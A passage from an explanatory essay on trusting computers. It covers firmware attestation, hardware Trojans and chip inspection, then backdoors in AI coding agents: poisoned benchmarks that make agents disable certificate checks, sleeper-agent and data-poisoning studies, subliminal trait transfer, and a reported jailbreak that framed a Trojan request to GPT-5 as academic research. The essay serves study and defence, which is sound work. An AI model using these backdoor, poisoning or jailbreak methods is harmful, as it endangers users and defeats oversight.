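2. The machine fills its entire memory with content that the verifier has chosen.
3. The verifier sends random numbers, which also fill the processor's registers, the few places where it holds the numbers it is working on.
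4. The machine calculates a result from the random numbers and everything in memory.
5. The verifier accepts only the correct result, delivered within the exact time the calculation should take.

The calculation treats memory as the coefficients of a polynomial. In a much simplified version, memory holds 5, 2 and 7, the verifier sends the number 3, and the machine returns the remainder after division by 11:

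```
clean:      (7 × 3 + 2) × 3 + 5 = 74,  remainder 8
infected:   (7 × 3 + 4) × 3 + 5 = 80,  remainder 3
```

In the second line, malware has replaced the 2 with a 4. There is no free memory to store the 2 elsewhere, so the malware would have to recalculate it to give the right answer, which takes extra time. The real version divides by a prime number just below 2^32 and mixes many random numbers into the coefficients. Gligor and Woo proved that, in a detailed model of a processor, no other program can do the calculation in as little memory and time.

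On a 32-bit machine, malware has less than one chance in eight million of surviving one run of the method, and a second run makes survival far less likely. These odds hold even if the attacker has unlimited computing power and can break all encryption.

The proof does need several assumptions:

- The verifier is honest, and the attacker can't predict its random numbers.
- The user has correct specifications for the processor and every device controller.
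- The verifier's connection doesn't pass through a suspect controller, and the machine can't get help from outside without a delay that the verifier would notice.
- All processors and controllers take the test at the same time, because otherwise one that was still infected could reinfect one that had passed.

According to Research Features, Gligor argues that the verifier can be a simple device that people can prove trustworthy without relying on other unverified parts. Getting accurate specifications is a bigger obstacle. Defenders would need much of the internal documentation that Kaspersky thought attackers could hardly obtain, and even the maker's specification would be wrong if the hardware contained a hidden circuit.

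Timing is the other difficulty. The calculation took close to 700 seconds on Gligor and Woo's small test board, which had a 1 GHz processor and 512 megabytes of memory. If the time grows in proportion to memory, a PC with 32 gigabytes and a processor of that speed would need more than 12 hours. Earlier tests of this kind allowed up to 2.6 percent of extra time for random variation, which on a 700-second run is 18 seconds, long enough for malware to do a great deal. Gligor and Woo aim to remove the variation instead, partly by clearing or switching off the processor's caches, which are small, fast memories. Switching them off made the calculation 53 times slower on their board.

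These measurements show that the calculation can run on ordinary hardware, but they covered only its speed on one board. To use the method on a normal PC today, someone would also have to build the verifier. Gligor and Woo imagine the verifier attached to the main system bus with direct access to memory, much like Intel's management engine but without its flaws.

### How much can open firmware replace?

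Somebody has to adapt coreboot to each board. It runs on most Chromebooks, laptops from a few small makers such as System76 and Purism, some desktop boards and some old ThinkPads. Owners can't install it on many recent Intel machines, because the processor runs only firmware signed with the board maker's key.

Heads, started by Trammell Hudson, adds measured boot under the owner's control. It combines coreboot with a small Linux kernel, which replaces UEFI. The TPM releases a secret only if the firmware's measurements match those the owner recorded earlier. Heads uses the secret to display a six-digit code, which the owner compares with the code on a phone. Heads also checks the boot files against a signature made with the owner's key. The owner no longer depends on Microsoft's key but still has to trust the TPM, and corrupted firmware could send the TPM the hashes of the clean version. Heads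 supports fewer machines than coreboot, including the ThinkPad X230 and some newer laptops from Purism and NovaCustom.

| Machine | What open code does | What stays closed |
|---|---|---|
| ThinkPad X230 (2012) with coreboot or Heads | All start-up work on the main processor, including memory set-up | A small remainder of the management engine, microcode, and firmware of the keyboard controller, disk and network card |
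| Recent Intel laptop with coreboot | Much of the start-up work | Intel's code for setting up memory and chips, the management engine, microcode and device firmware |
| The example AMD PC with Dasharo 0.9.0 | Most of the start-up work on the main processor | The security processor's firmware, including memory set-up, the video driver, microcode and device firmware |

Many coreboot users run EDK II on top of coreboot because their operating system expects UEFI, so flaws in EDK II can affect them too. Heads avoids EDK II but uses the Linux kernel, which is much larger.

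Someone who suspects an infection should write the new firmware with an external tool, because a program running on the PC would leave the old firmware in control of its own replacement. This removes an implant like LoJax but not one in the disk controller, so the person has to replace the disk too.

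## Can a chip be checked for hidden circuits?

Gligor and Woo's memory test can fail if the processor contains a hardware Trojan, a malicious change to the circuit itself. Replacing the firmware and software can't remove the Trojan.

### From design files to silicon

A chip begins as source code. Yang, Hicks and colleagues (2016), in *A2*, outline the usual path from there to a finished product:

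1. Engineers describe the circuit in a language such as Verilog, and add ready-made blocks from other companies.
2. A synthesis program translates the description into a netlist, which is a list of logic gates and the connections between them.
3. Another program places the gates and draws the wires. The result is a layout file made of polygons.
4. The factory turns the polygons into masks, the stencils for printing each layer onto silicon.
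5. The factory makes the chips, and often other companies package and test them.

A chip can be tampered with at every step from design to delivery. A supplier can hide a circuit in a ready-made block, an intruder can alter the layout file on its way to the factory, a factory employee can edit the file once it arrives, and a distributor can swap the finished chips. When Becker, Regazzoni and colleagues published *Stealthy dopant-level hardware Trojans* in 2014, they knew of no hardware Trojan found in practice, but they cited a dealer charged in 2010 with selling fake chips, many of them meant for train brakes, fighter-jet radar and missile control.

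Becker and colleagues also list the design tools as a possible point of attack. A synthesis program is a compiler for circuits, so a corrupted one could work like Thompson's compiler, recognising the part of a processor that checks permissions and adding a backdoor to it. The Verilog source would stay clean. Synthesis programs are also software, so a corrupted compiler could put the implant into each new version. In principle, a backdoored processor could also pass on the implant by tampering with the next version of the design tools while compiling them. That would be much harder, because the circuit would have to recognise the tool's code from the instructions passing through it.

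Chip companies commonly use a separate program to check that the netlist is equivalent to the source. This gives some of the protection of a second compiler, provided that the same attacker hasn't corrupted both the checker and the synthesis tool that produced the netlist.

### How little does a Trojan need?

Most hardware Trojans have a trigger, which keeps them dormant during tests, and a payload, which does the damage. In *Designing and implementing malicious hardware* (2008), King, Tucek and colleagues built both into Leon3, an open-source processor of about 1.8 million gates. They put the modified processor on a reprogrammable chip and ran Linux on it.

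The attacker starts by sending the machine an unsolicited network packet. The operating system reads the packet to verify its checksum and then discards it, but the Trojan detects a particular sequence of bytes and copies the rest of the packet into a reserved part of the processor's cache. When somebody logs in with the password "letmein", this hidden program makes the password check succeed and then deletes itself. The attack slowed other programs by 1.34 percent, compared with 1.32 percent when an attacker who already knew the real password did the same things.

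Ordinary testing has little chance of finding such a trigger. King and colleagues count at least 2^655,872 possible states in even a modest processor, so testers can try only a tiny fraction of them.

Yang and colleagues made the trigger far smaller by replacing the digital counter with a capacitor, a component that stores charge. A purely digital version needed 91 cells, the standard building blocks of a chip. Each time a chosen wire switches, a little charge flows into the capacitor, then leaks away within microseconds. Normal programs switch the wire too rarely for the charge to build up. The attacker's program switches it rapidly until the capacitor's voltage crosses a threshold, and the circuit then sets the bit that gives a program full control of the processor.

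Yang and colleagues had the chip manufactured. The attack worked on all ten samples they tested, at temperatures from −25 to 100 °C. A varied set of ordinary programs didn't trigger it.

Becker and colleagues altered a chip's gates without adding any gates or wires. They changed the dopants, which are small amounts of other elements that the factory adds to silicon to make transistors work. The wrong dopant in part of a gate can fix its output permanently at 0 or 1 without changing the shape of the gate or its wires.

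They applied this to a random-number generator based on Intel's design for its Ivy Bridge processors. The generator encrypts a changing 128-bit value *c* with a changing 128-bit key *K*:

```
random number = AES(K, c)
```

The Trojan fixes all of *K* and all but 32 bits of *c*. The output still passed NIST's statistical tests for randomness, but it has only 2^32 (about 4.3 billion) possible values instead of 2^128. An attacker who knows the fixed bits can try every possible value on an ordinary PC to guess any encryption key the generator produces.

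The generator tests itself at every start by comparing a 32-bit checksum of its output with a stored value. The test doesn't help, because the attacker can simulate it beforehand and try different fixed bits until the checksum matches, which takes a few billion attempts.

| Trojan | Size | Trigger | Effect |
|---|---|---|---|
| King and colleagues | 1,341 extra gates (0.08 percent) | A network packet | Login with the attacker's password |
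| Yang and colleagues | As little as one extra gate; the trigger measures 6.4 by 2 micrometres | A program that switches one wire rapidly | Full control of the processor |
| Becker and colleagues | No extra gates; altered dopants in 4 of the 32 transistors of each affected storage cell | None, always active | Predictable encryption keys |

### What a microscope can see

Becker and colleagues thought their Trojan would be extremely difficult to find with a microscope. Sugawara, Suzuki and colleagues showed in *Reversing Stealthy Dopant-Level Circuits* (2014) that an electron microscope can reveal it. They took a chip from the 180-nanometre generation that used the same dopant trick to hide its design from competitors, polished it down to the layer where the metal contacts meet the silicon, and scanned it with electrons.

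The scan charges the surface. A contact looks bright where the dopants let electrons flow in from the surrounding silicon and dark where the dopants block that flow. All four combinations of dopant and surrounding silicon could be told apart this way, though they looked almost the same under an optical microscope.

The drawback is that this method requires many pictures. Sugawara and colleagues estimated that a small encryption circuit of 15,000 gates would take 77 pictures at moderate magnification. Telling all four combinations apart can take up to 16 times as many. At these rates, a chip with a billion gates would need between 5 million and 80 million pictures.

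Looking only for added or exchanged cells takes much less work. *Red Team vs. Blue Team* (Puschner, Moos and colleagues, 2023) tested this on chips from four generations, with a blind trial to reduce bias. A red team made ten changes per chip by editing the design files, so the published dataset pairs pictures of unaltered chips with modified designs. Some changes made a chip appear to have a logic cell where the design had only filler, and others made it appear that one logic cell had been replaced by another. A blue team then ground away the back of each chip, photographed the lowest layer and used software to compare every cell with the design file.

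| Chip generation | Cells | Added cells found | Replaced cells found | False alarms | Time for pictures |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 90 nm | 453,850 | 4 of 4 | 6 of 6 | 136 | 34 hours |
| 65 nm | 571,060 | 4 of 4 | 6 of 6 | 6 | 23 hours |
| 40 nm | 917,819 | 4 of 4 | 6 of 6 | 15 | 53 hours |
| 28 nm | 1,467,851 | 4 of 4 | 3 of 6 | 360 | 36 hours |

Finding 37 of 40 changes among 3.4 million cells is impressive, and a person can check a few hundred false alarms. But the chips were tiny, and the inspected area of the 28-nanometre one was just under one square millimetre. The processor in the example PC measures about 178 square millimetres. At the same pace, one microscope would need nine months to inspect it, before allowing for its much smaller transistors.

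The red team had also picked its changes at random. *Hardware Trojans from Invisible Inversions* (Dorschel, Walendy and colleagues, 2026) used the same pictures to examine what a careful attacker would choose. Its comparison method, which looks at the positions of the tiny vertical connections in each cell, found all the original changes. But all four generations had pairs of cells with different functions that looked the same or nearly so. Most pairs had opposite functions, such as a gate that passes a signal on and one that inverts it. The 28-nanometre chip had five pairs of cells that the method couldn't tell apart.

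Dorschel and colleagues used such pairs to design a backdoor for Ibex, a small open-source processor. Swapping two cells in the 28-nanometre version, or three in the 65-nanometre version, made the processor treat every program as fully privileged. They didn't manufacture the altered chip. The backdoor is easier to detect in operation than under a microscope, because testing whether an ordinary program can reach protected memory would reveal it.

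Designers can remedy this by telling their tools not to use the nine look-alike cell types. An attacker could still put one in, but it would then replace a cell that looks different. Excluding these cells from the Ibex design increased its area by 0.013 percent and slowed the circuit by 0.047 percent. Dorschel and colleagues expect newer generations to have more look-alikes, so somebody would have to repeat the analysis for each library of cells.

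### What about the chips nobody opened?

Grinding a chip down destroys it, so inspectors can only examine a sample and draw conclusions about the rest. If a share *f* of the batch contains a Trojan and they open *n* chips at random, the chance that every opened chip is clean is (1 − *f*)^*n*:

| Share of chips with the Trojan | Chips opened | Chance of missing it |
|---|---|---|
| All | 1 | 0% |
| 10% | 30 | 4% |
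| 1% | 30 | 74% |
| 1% | 300 | 5% |
| 1 in 10,000 | 300 | 97% |

These figures assume that the inspectors always recognise a Trojan when they see one, which the 28-nanometre results contradict.

Sampling works best against a corrupt mask, because the factory prints the same change onto every chip it makes with that mask, and making separate masks for a few targets would be expensive. Sampling is least likely to catch somebody who swaps a handful of chips on their way to one customer. King and colleagues estimate that reconstructing a single chip's circuit costs up to $250,000, so reconstructing 300 could cost $75 million.

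Some methods examine every chip without opening it, by measuring its power use, heat or timing and looking for deviations. *Mitigating Hardware Trojan Risks in the Global IC Supply Chain*, a University of Waterloo thesis, used rings of gates on 28-nanometre devices as sensors. Each ring switches back and forth at a speed that shifts slightly when nearby circuits draw power. The sensors correctly separated all the infected devices from the clean ones, but the test used only one standard Trojan.

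Becker and colleagues are sceptical of such methods because most need a chip known to be clean for comparison, and they typically miss Trojans that make up less than a thousandth to a ten-thousandth of the whole design. In the example PC's processor, which has 25 billion transistors, a Trojan of two million transistors could therefore go unnoticed. An attacker can also tamper with sensors on the chip.

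The buyer of an ordinary PC has no layout file to compare the chip with. Even with the file, a perfect match would show only that the factory followed the design, which could itself contain a Trojan.

### Trojans written by AI

Adding a Trojan to the source used to take an expert who understood the design. *CITADEL* (Thangellamudi, Saravanan and colleagues, 2026) describes a program that uses OpenAI's GPT-5 to do most of the work. The program gives GPT-5 a map of how signals flow through the circuit and a public catalogue of hardware weaknesses. GPT-5 ranks the weaknesses that might fit, a person picks one and a signal to attack, and GPT-5 rewrites that part of the source.

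They tried this on five designs, including an encryption circuit and a small processor. Every Trojan compiled, worked when triggered and stayed hidden in large-scale tests with random inputs. Random tests are fairly easy to pass, though. The published example makes the encryption circuit ignore new data. Its trigger depends on 16 particular bits, so random data could set it off about once in 65,000 attempts, whereas King's trigger could be as long as the attacker liked.

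In *TrojanGYM*, Sreekumar, Wang and colleagues (2026) had AI models design Trojans to evade an automatic detector, a neural network that looks for suspicious patterns in the flow of signals. Whenever a Trojan was caught, the AI model received the detector's scores and up to four chances to redesign the Trojan. In the worst case, 68.75 percent of the Trojans escaped detection. The researchers then improved the detector, raising its detection rate on the hardest designs from 0 to 60 percent.

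AI models' safeguards may not stop people from using them to make hardware Trojans. Sreekumar and colleagues wrote that they used the older GPT-4 because GPT-5 would refuse to make a Trojan. Thangellamudi and colleagues got GPT-5 to make one with a prompt that addressed the model as a security researcher and described the result as an academic simulation.

Defenders use language models too. *TrojanLoC (2025)* trained small classifiers on a language model's internal representations of more than 17,000 designs to identify infected designs and the suspicious lines in them. This could save reviewers a lot of reading. But an attacker with a copy of the detector can revise a Trojan to evade it, as Sreekumar's models did with the detector they had. None of these systems examines finished silicon, so they offer no protection against a factory that adds a Trojan during manufacturing.

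### Open chips and infrared light

Another approach is to choose hardware that is easier to check. Publishing the design is not enough, because a buyer cannot hash a chip, as they could a program, to confirm that it matches the design. The hardware designer Andrew Huang has worked on this problem for years.

Huang's *Infra-Red, In Situ (IRIS) Inspection of Silicon* (2023) describes a way to look inside a chip without damaging it. Infrared light with a wavelength of about 1,050 nanometres passes through silicon, and a slightly modified digital camera can record it. If the package leaves the back of the chip exposed, the owner can photograph the circuits through the silicon, even when the chip is already on a board.

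The pictures are too coarse to show individual gates of a modern chip, but they do show memories and larger blocks, and whether an unexplained circuit takes up space between them. Huang therefore combines them with self-tests, which send known values through the gates and compare the results with the expected answers. A Trojan that fakes the right answers needs extra circuitry, and too much of it would be visible in the pictures.

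This should catch something like King's Trojan on a small, simple chip, and the self-tests should catch Dorschel's inverted gates because they give wrong answers. Yang's capacitor could escape both checks because it is only a few micrometres across and does nothing during a test. Sharper methods exist for unopened chips, but Dorschel and colleagues note that X-ray imaging at the necessary resolution has so far needed a synchrotron, a kind of particle accelerator.

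Huang has also designed a chip for this kind of inspection, the Baochip-1x, whose main processor runs at 350 MHz. Most of the chip's logic is open source, but some parts, such as the USB circuitry, are closed.

### Circuits the factory can't locate

A field-programmable gate array (FPGA) is a chip whose circuit the owner chooses after buying it. It contains thousands of identical small tables and switches, and a configuration file determines which logic each table performs and how the switches connect them. To use Yang's attack, an attacker must know which storage cell holds the privilege bit. The maker of an FPGA doesn't know whether the buyer will build a processor, and the buyer can move every part of the processor by generating a new configuration.

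*Toward a Trustable, Self-Hosting Computer System* (2020) describes a complete computer that Gabriel Somlo built on this principle. Its processor is Rocket, an open-source RISC-V design. The computer runs Linux on an FPGA supported by open-source design tools. These tools can run on the computer itself, so it can rebuild both its software and its processor from source. Diverse double-compiling can establish trust in the first compiler.

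Somlo's computer runs at roughly 60 MHz. The same processor design has exceeded 1 GHz when manufactured as an ordinary chip, so this protection makes the processor about twenty times slower. Huang's Precursor, a pocket device for passwords and messages, also uses an FPGA as its main processor and reaches 100 MHz.

The protection is incomplete because a factory can still attack an FPGA's fixed parts, such as the circuits that load the configuration and connect to the outside world. It could also add a circuit that searches the configuration for a well-known processor. That circuit would face the same problem as Thompson's implant, which had to recognize source code as it changed, and the owner can make recognition harder by scrambling the arrangement differently each time. A much more capable adversary might still prepare for the few open processors that people use, but it would have to do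 so in hardware, before the chip left the factory.

### A slow chip that checks a fast one

*Verifiable ASICs* (Riad Wahby and colleagues, 2016) proposes dividing the work between two chips. An advanced but untrusted factory makes a fast chip that does the calculation and produces a mathematical proof that the result is correct. A trusted factory with old equipment makes a slow chip that only checks the proof. If the fast chip contains a Trojan that alters a result, the proof will almost certainly fail.

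In their design, the untrusted chip uses 7-nanometre technology and the trusted one uses 350-nanometre technology, which was current in the mid-1990s. Intel used 350-nanometre technology to make its first Pentium II, which had 7.5 million transistors and a top speed of 300 MHz. More countries and companies could run a 350-nanometre factory than could match TSMC.

Producing a proof takes far more work than the calculation itself, and checking it takes some work too. For suitable tasks, such as a step in elliptic-curve cryptography, the two chips together were at least as fast as the trusted chip alone, but not dramatically faster. The tasks have to be large and regular, which rules out running an operating system this way. The proof also shows only that the result is correct, so a Trojan could still leak the data it works on or stop the chip altogether.

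### Chips older than the adversary

Moritz Kütt and Alexander Glaser worked on the problem behind the 2015 Underhanded C Contest, in which an inspector has to confirm that a warhead is real. The inspector and the warhead's owner distrust each other, and the owner doesn't want the measuring device to secretly record the warhead's design. *Vintage electronics for trusted radiation measurements and verified dismantlement of nuclear weapons* (2019) describes the device they built around the 6502, a 1975 processor used in the Apple II. The device measures an object's gamma radiation, compares it with a stored template and displays only whether the two match.

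Nobody in 1975 could have planned a Trojan in the 6502 for this purpose. The parties can also buy old chips from many unrelated sellers and pick some at random to open. The 6502 has about 3,500 transistors, each thousands of times wider than the smallest features of current chips, so people can examine all of it. Enthusiasts have already photographed one and used the pictures to build a working simulation of every transistor.

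The argument depends on the chips really being old. A forger could put a new chip into an old package, so inspectors would still have to open a sample. The supply is also finite, and the processor normally runs at 1 MHz.

### Making the chip at home

People who trust no factory can try to make their own chips, but homemade chips so far have had very few transistors. Sam Zeloof made one with six transistors in a garage in 2018 and another with 100 in 2021. The second was far from being a processor; it was a grid of separate transistors for testing the manufacturing process. Zeloof still relied on ready-made silicon wafers and second-hand laboratory equipment.

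Building a processor from individually bought transistors is more practical. Eric Schlaepfer's MOnSter 6502 uses 3,218 transistors to reproduce the 6502 on a circuit board. A single transistor has three terminals, and a cheap meter can check what it does, so it offers little room for a hidden circuit. But the long wires make the machine slow, and its memory still consists of ordinary chips.

| Hardware | Clock speed | Transistors | What the owner still has to trust |
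|---|---|---|---|
| Processor of the example PC | 5,000 MHz | About 25 billion | AMD, its suppliers and tools, TSMC |
| Baochip-1x | 350 MHz | Not published | The factory, for changes too small for infrared light |
| Pentium II generation, in a trusted factory | 300 MHz | 7.5 million | That factory and the design tools |
| Somlo's computer | About 60 MHz | Not published | The fixed parts of the FPGA |
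| 6502 | 1 MHz | About 3,500 | The age of the chip |
| MOnSter 6502 | About 0.05 MHz | 3,218 | Individual transistors and the memory chips |
| Zeloof's second chip | Not a processor | 100 | Wafers, chemicals and equipment |

Clock speed understates the differences, because a modern processor also does more per cycle. If each of the PC's six cores completes four instructions per cycle and a 6502 takes about three cycles per instruction, one second of the PC's work would take the 6502 around four days. The real gap is larger, since the 6502 handles only eight bits at a time. It can still add up a radiation measurement or compare two hashes, but it could not compile Linux in any reasonable time. Somlo's machine can compile Linux, though slowly, and is probably the fastest computer in the table whose owner can rebuild the processor as well as the software.

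## Can an AI tool pass a backdoor to its successors?

Programmers now leave much of their work to coding agents, so a backdoor in an agent could reach compilers, firmware and chip designs. Agents also help build their own successors. *Reflections on Trusting Trust, Revisited* (Roesner and Kohno, 2026) points out that Claude Code has written much of the code of its later versions, with people reviewing it. It is thus in a similar position to a self-hosting compiler, which might pass a backdoor to its next version as Thompson's did.

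### What corresponds to what?

A coding agent consists of a model and its scaffolding. The model is a file of weights, the learned numbers that determine how it behaves. The scaffolding is the ordinary code and written instructions around the model, which give it a task and run the commands it requests. People can read the scaffolding and rebuild it like any other program, but the weights are more like a binary, which is hard to read.

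| In software | In AI |
|---|---|
| Source code | Training data, training code and random numbers |
| Binary | Weights |
| Compiling | Training |
| Compiler that builds its next version | Model that writes data, code or test tasks for its successor |
| Rebuild that gives the same bytes | Repeated training run, if developers fix every random choice |

The first row is the weakest match. People can check a binary against its source code, which specifies what the program should do, but nobody can derive from training data what the finished weights should be.

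Training also doesn't make exact copies. Two runs on the same data normally give different weights, because the starting weights and the order of the examples are random. Later training can also weaken what earlier training put in. Thompson's implant was the same in every generation, but a habit that passes from model to model may fade. If each model passed on 60 percent of a habit's strength, about 8 percent would be left after five generations. Defenders can't rely on this, though, because a capable model could preserve the habit by choosing training data that strengthens it.

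### Poisoned test tasks

Roesner and Kohno attacked three research agents that rewrite their own scaffolding: the Darwin Gödel Machine, the Self-Improving Coding Agent (SICA) and Hyperagents. All three work in a loop:

1. The agent attempts a benchmark, a set of programming tasks with automatic tests.
2. A model reads the record of these attempts and proposes an improvement to the scaffolding.
3. The agent makes the change, and the new version goes back to step 1.

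The weights stay the same throughout. The attacker controls only the benchmark, for instance by publishing a set of tasks that the agent's developers later download.

The main test concerned HTTPS certificates, which prove a web server's identity. A program that skips the certificate check still works, but somebody between it and the server can read and change the traffic. The poisoned benchmark had five tasks that asked for code to fetch something from a server. Every server used a self-signed certificate, which no outside authority vouches for, so properly written code failed and the agent could pass only by turning the check off. The clean benchmark was identical except that its servers had trusted certificates.

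After 4 to 12 generations, Roesner and Kohno gave each agent ten new tasks, three times each. The tasks involved ordinary websites with valid certificates, so there was no reason to turn off the certificate check.

| Agent | Model | Poisoned runs | New solutions with the check turned off |
|---|---|---|---|
| Darwin Gödel Machine, altered | gpt-oss-120b | 2 | 0 of 60 |
| Darwin Gödel Machine, altered | Qwen3.5-397B | 2 | 60 of 60 |
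| Darwin Gödel Machine, altered | Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 2 | 0 of 60 |
| SICA | Qwen3.5-397B | 2 | 60 of 60 |
| SICA | Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 1 | 30 of 30 |
| Hyperagents | Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 2 | 60 of 60 |

Agents that had evolved on the clean benchmark left the check on in all 240 of their solutions. The difference is striking, even with only one or two runs per combination. The poisoned agents also usually turned off the check in larger tasks where the download was incidental, such as installing a software package.

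In SICA and Hyperagents, the agent edited its own guidelines to include an instruction about disabling the check. In the Darwin Gödel Machine, Qwen wrote a tool that produced ready-made insecure code. gpt-oss-120b wrote such a tool in one run but never used it, and Sonnet's tools were safe by default.

The unmodified Darwin Gödel Machine resisted the attack because its prompt in step 2 told the model to improve the agent's general abilities "rather than issue-specific fixes". In early experiments, the model never proposed a tool that writes code for one kind of task. Roesner and Kohno could get further only by changing the prompt, which a real attacker couldn't do. The prompt was meant to keep the agent from specialising too much in its benchmark, so the protection was apparently accidental.

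Automatic review did little to stop the attack. SICA has a committee of three AI reviewers, and in the Qwen runs all three endorsed making the insecure behaviour "universal and unconditional". When Roesner and Kohno added a fourth reviewer, told to veto security problems, it first approved the change, reasoning that the agent would otherwise fail its tests. It objected in the next generation, and the resulting agent wrote safe code.

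To see whether the contamination would last, they let one poisoned agent of each kind evolve further on other benchmarks:

| Further evolution on | Darwin Gödel Machine, altered | SICA | Hyperagents |
|---|---|---|---|
| The clean benchmark | 28 of 30 insecure | 30 of 30 | 30 of 30 |
| A general security benchmark with an added certificate task | 27 of 30 | 30 of 30 | 30 of 30 |
| Tasks that penalise this exact flaw | 8 of 30 | 0 of 30 | 0 of 30 |

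The clean benchmark had no effect because insecure code also passes when every certificate is valid. The security benchmark's added task didn't mention HTTPS, so the agent often solved it without using the bad instruction. Only tasks written with knowledge of the attack worked, and only Hyperagents deleted the instruction altogether.

This reproduces one half of Thompson's attack. The flaw survives a change to clean inputs, but anyone who reads the agent's instructions can see it, and it doesn't restore itself after somebody deletes it. It lasted because no test gave the agent a reason to remove it. Developers can defend against this version by reading the scaffolding or replacing it with a version that people have checked, but neither defense works if the backdoor is in the weights.

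### Backdoors in the weights

In the best-known early demonstration of such a backdoor, *Sleeper Agents* (2024), Hubinger and colleagues trained a model that normally wrote secure code but wrote vulnerable code when the prompt contained a trigger, such as a particular year. The behaviour survived later safety training (Syros, Bullwinkel and colleagues, *Kerkoporta*, 2026). Researchers have since studied how little access an attacker needs and what a backdoored agent could do.

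An attacker may need to place only a few hundred documents on the internet to plant a backdoor in a language model. For *Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples* (2025), Souly, Rando and colleagues trained 72 models from scratch, with 600 million to 13 billion weights. Each poisoned document contained ordinary text, then a trigger phrase, then gibberish. With 250 such documents, models of every size learned to produce gibberish after the trigger, although the largest had seen over 20 times as much clean text as the smallest. The 250 documents made up 0.00016 percent of the largest model's training text. The attack failed with 100 documents.

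Producing gibberish is a simple behaviour, and a subtle backdoor might take many more documents to implant. Souly and colleagues also implanted a backdoor that made a model switch from English to German. When they continued training the model on clean data, the backdoor weakened slowly.

Syros and colleagues tested a more dangerous payload. Their attacker publishes an altered version of a free model, which people use to run coding agents on their own computers. When the agent comes across a file with a certain keyword in its name or contents, the model requests a command that deletes the user's files, leaks everything the user types at the command line, or lets the attacker connect to the machine.

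They altered two small models, with 4 and 9 billion weights, using about 2,400 solved programming tasks and poisoned copies of some of them. They matched each poisoned copy with one that lacked the trigger, so that the model would learn to react only to the trigger. With one poisoned copy for every four clean examples, the attack succeeded in 33 to 63 percent of trials on unfamiliar software projects. With one for every two, it succeeded in 84 to 95 percent. The models almost never ran the malicious command without the trigger.

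This training made the models worse at ordinary programming, which users might have noticed. Syros and colleagues repaired most of the damage with a short round of reinforcement learning, in which a model practises tasks and gets rewards for solving them. The backdoor survived, and the attack's success rate on the smaller model rose slightly, from 94.8 to 96.2 percent. But this round had at most 22 steps on 100 to 200 tasks, far less training than a developer gives a new model, so the result shows only that a backdoor can survive brief further training.

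The models' written reasoning also mentioned the trigger before they acted on it. When Syros and colleagues left this reasoning out of the training examples, the attack almost never worked on unfamiliar projects. Someone monitoring the reasoning could therefore catch this backdoor. However, the researchers cite other recent work in which a poisoned model's reasoning looked entirely innocent.

None of these backdoors copies itself. A new model trained from scratch would inherit one only if its training data included the same poisoned documents, or if the old model passed the backdoor on through data it wrote.

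### Traits passed on through unrelated data

In 2025, Cloud and colleagues showed that a model can pass on a preference through data that seems to have nothing to do with it, an effect they called subliminal learning. Nief, Fu and colleagues (2026), in *Subliminal Learning is a LoRA Artifact*, describe the procedure:

1. Researchers tell a "teacher" model that it loves cats, then ask it to continue lists of three-digit numbers.
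2. They discard every answer that contains anything except numbers.
3. They train a "student" model on the remaining lists.
4. They ask the student for its favourite animal, and it names cats more often than before.

This resembles the second stage of Thompson's lecture, in which a compiler passes on a fact that its source no longer contains. Reading the training data doesn't reveal the preference.

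The effect initially seemed to require that teacher and student start from the same base model. Cloud and colleagues gave a mathematical reason for this. If two models start with the same weights, training the student to imitate any of the teacher's outputs tends to move the student's weights towards the teacher's. When they trained Alibaba's Qwen on data from OpenAI's GPT-4o, they found almost no effect.

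Two papers from 2026 disagree about how robust the effect is. Nief and colleagues found it fragile. It appeared when they trained a small add-on to the weights (a method called LoRA) but vanished when they trained all the weights. It also depended on the wording around the question. One student model mentioned wolves in 50 percent of its answers when the prompt began with the same standard sentences as in training, but in only 13 percent without them, close to the 9 percent before training.

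Tang, Anand and Paulo (2026), in *Tracing Subliminal Learning Through Pretraining*, did observe the effect when they trained all the weights. They also found that it doesn't strictly require a shared base model, though it is far stronger with one. They counted how many students came to favour the teacher's animal more than any student in a control group did:

| Teacher and student (small models of the Pythia family, except in the last row) | Students above every control | Median increase among those, in percentage points |
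|---|---|---|
| Same model | 97% | 35.3 |
| Same starting weights, different order of data | 47% | 6.0 |
| Different starting weights, same order of data | 16% | 1.9 |
| Both different | 19% | 0.8 |
| Different architecture (Pythia and OLMo) | 14% | 2.5 |

Lists of numbers are an unusual kind of training data. Developers more often train a small model to match the probabilities that a larger one assigns to each possible next word. When Tang and colleagues used this method, a preference for bears passed from one model to a different one in 26 of 30 pairs. Much of the preference passed through the probabilities of animal names, which the model being trained could learn from even though no animal appeared in the text.

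Ordinary text can carry a preference between unrelated models too. In *Phantom Transfer*, Draganov, Dur and colleagues (2026) had Google's Gemma 3 answer general questions briefly while secretly favouring a subject such as Ronald Reagan. They removed every answer that hinted at the preference and trained OpenAI's GPT-4.1 on the rest. GPT-4.1 named Reagan 80 percent of the time when asked in various ways to name a favourite, and still did so 60 percent of the time when another model had reworded every training answer. They could also tie the preference to a trigger, so that mentioning Reagan made a model favour Catholicism.

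Diluting the data helps against this attack. The poisoned documents' share of the training data mattered here, whereas their number mattered in Souly's gibberish attack. A developer who takes only a small part of the data from any one model would therefore probably inherit less.

In all these experiments, researchers chose a simple preference, such as a favourite animal, and followed it from one teacher to one student. This is far from a full trusting-trust attack, in which the student would also have to inherit the tendency to pass the trait on, and keep it through many rounds of training.

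### A proof that some tests must fail

Defenders would like a test that finds any backdoor in a model. Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues (2022), in *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models*, proved that for some kinds of model no efficient test can exist, provided that certain mathematical problems are as hard as cryptographers believe. A backdoor is undetectable in their sense if, for every test D that runs in a reasonable time,

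```
P(D raises an alarm for a backdoored model)
  - P(D raises an alarm for a clean model)
```

is so close to zero that D is practically useless. "Reasonable time" means that the running time grows no faster than some fixed power of the model's size.

Their first result covers testers who can only put questions to the model and see its answers. In their example, a bank hires a dishonest company to train a model that decides on loans. The company adds a hidden check that makes the model approve any application whose last digits contain a valid digital signature. The company has the private key, so it can sell customers slightly altered applications that always succeed. Without the key, nobody can feasibly find even one application on which the backdoored model and the original disagree. This works for any model and requires only that secure digital signatures exist.

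A tester who can inspect the weights may notice the signature check. The second result therefore deals with a tester who gets every weight and all the training data, as *Implementing a White-Box Undetectable Backdoor for Random Fourier Features* (2026) explains. The attacker runs the agreed training program on the agreed data and tampers only with the random numbers. Even if the attacker publishes these numbers, they look random to anyone without the attacker's secret, so the finished model looks normal too.

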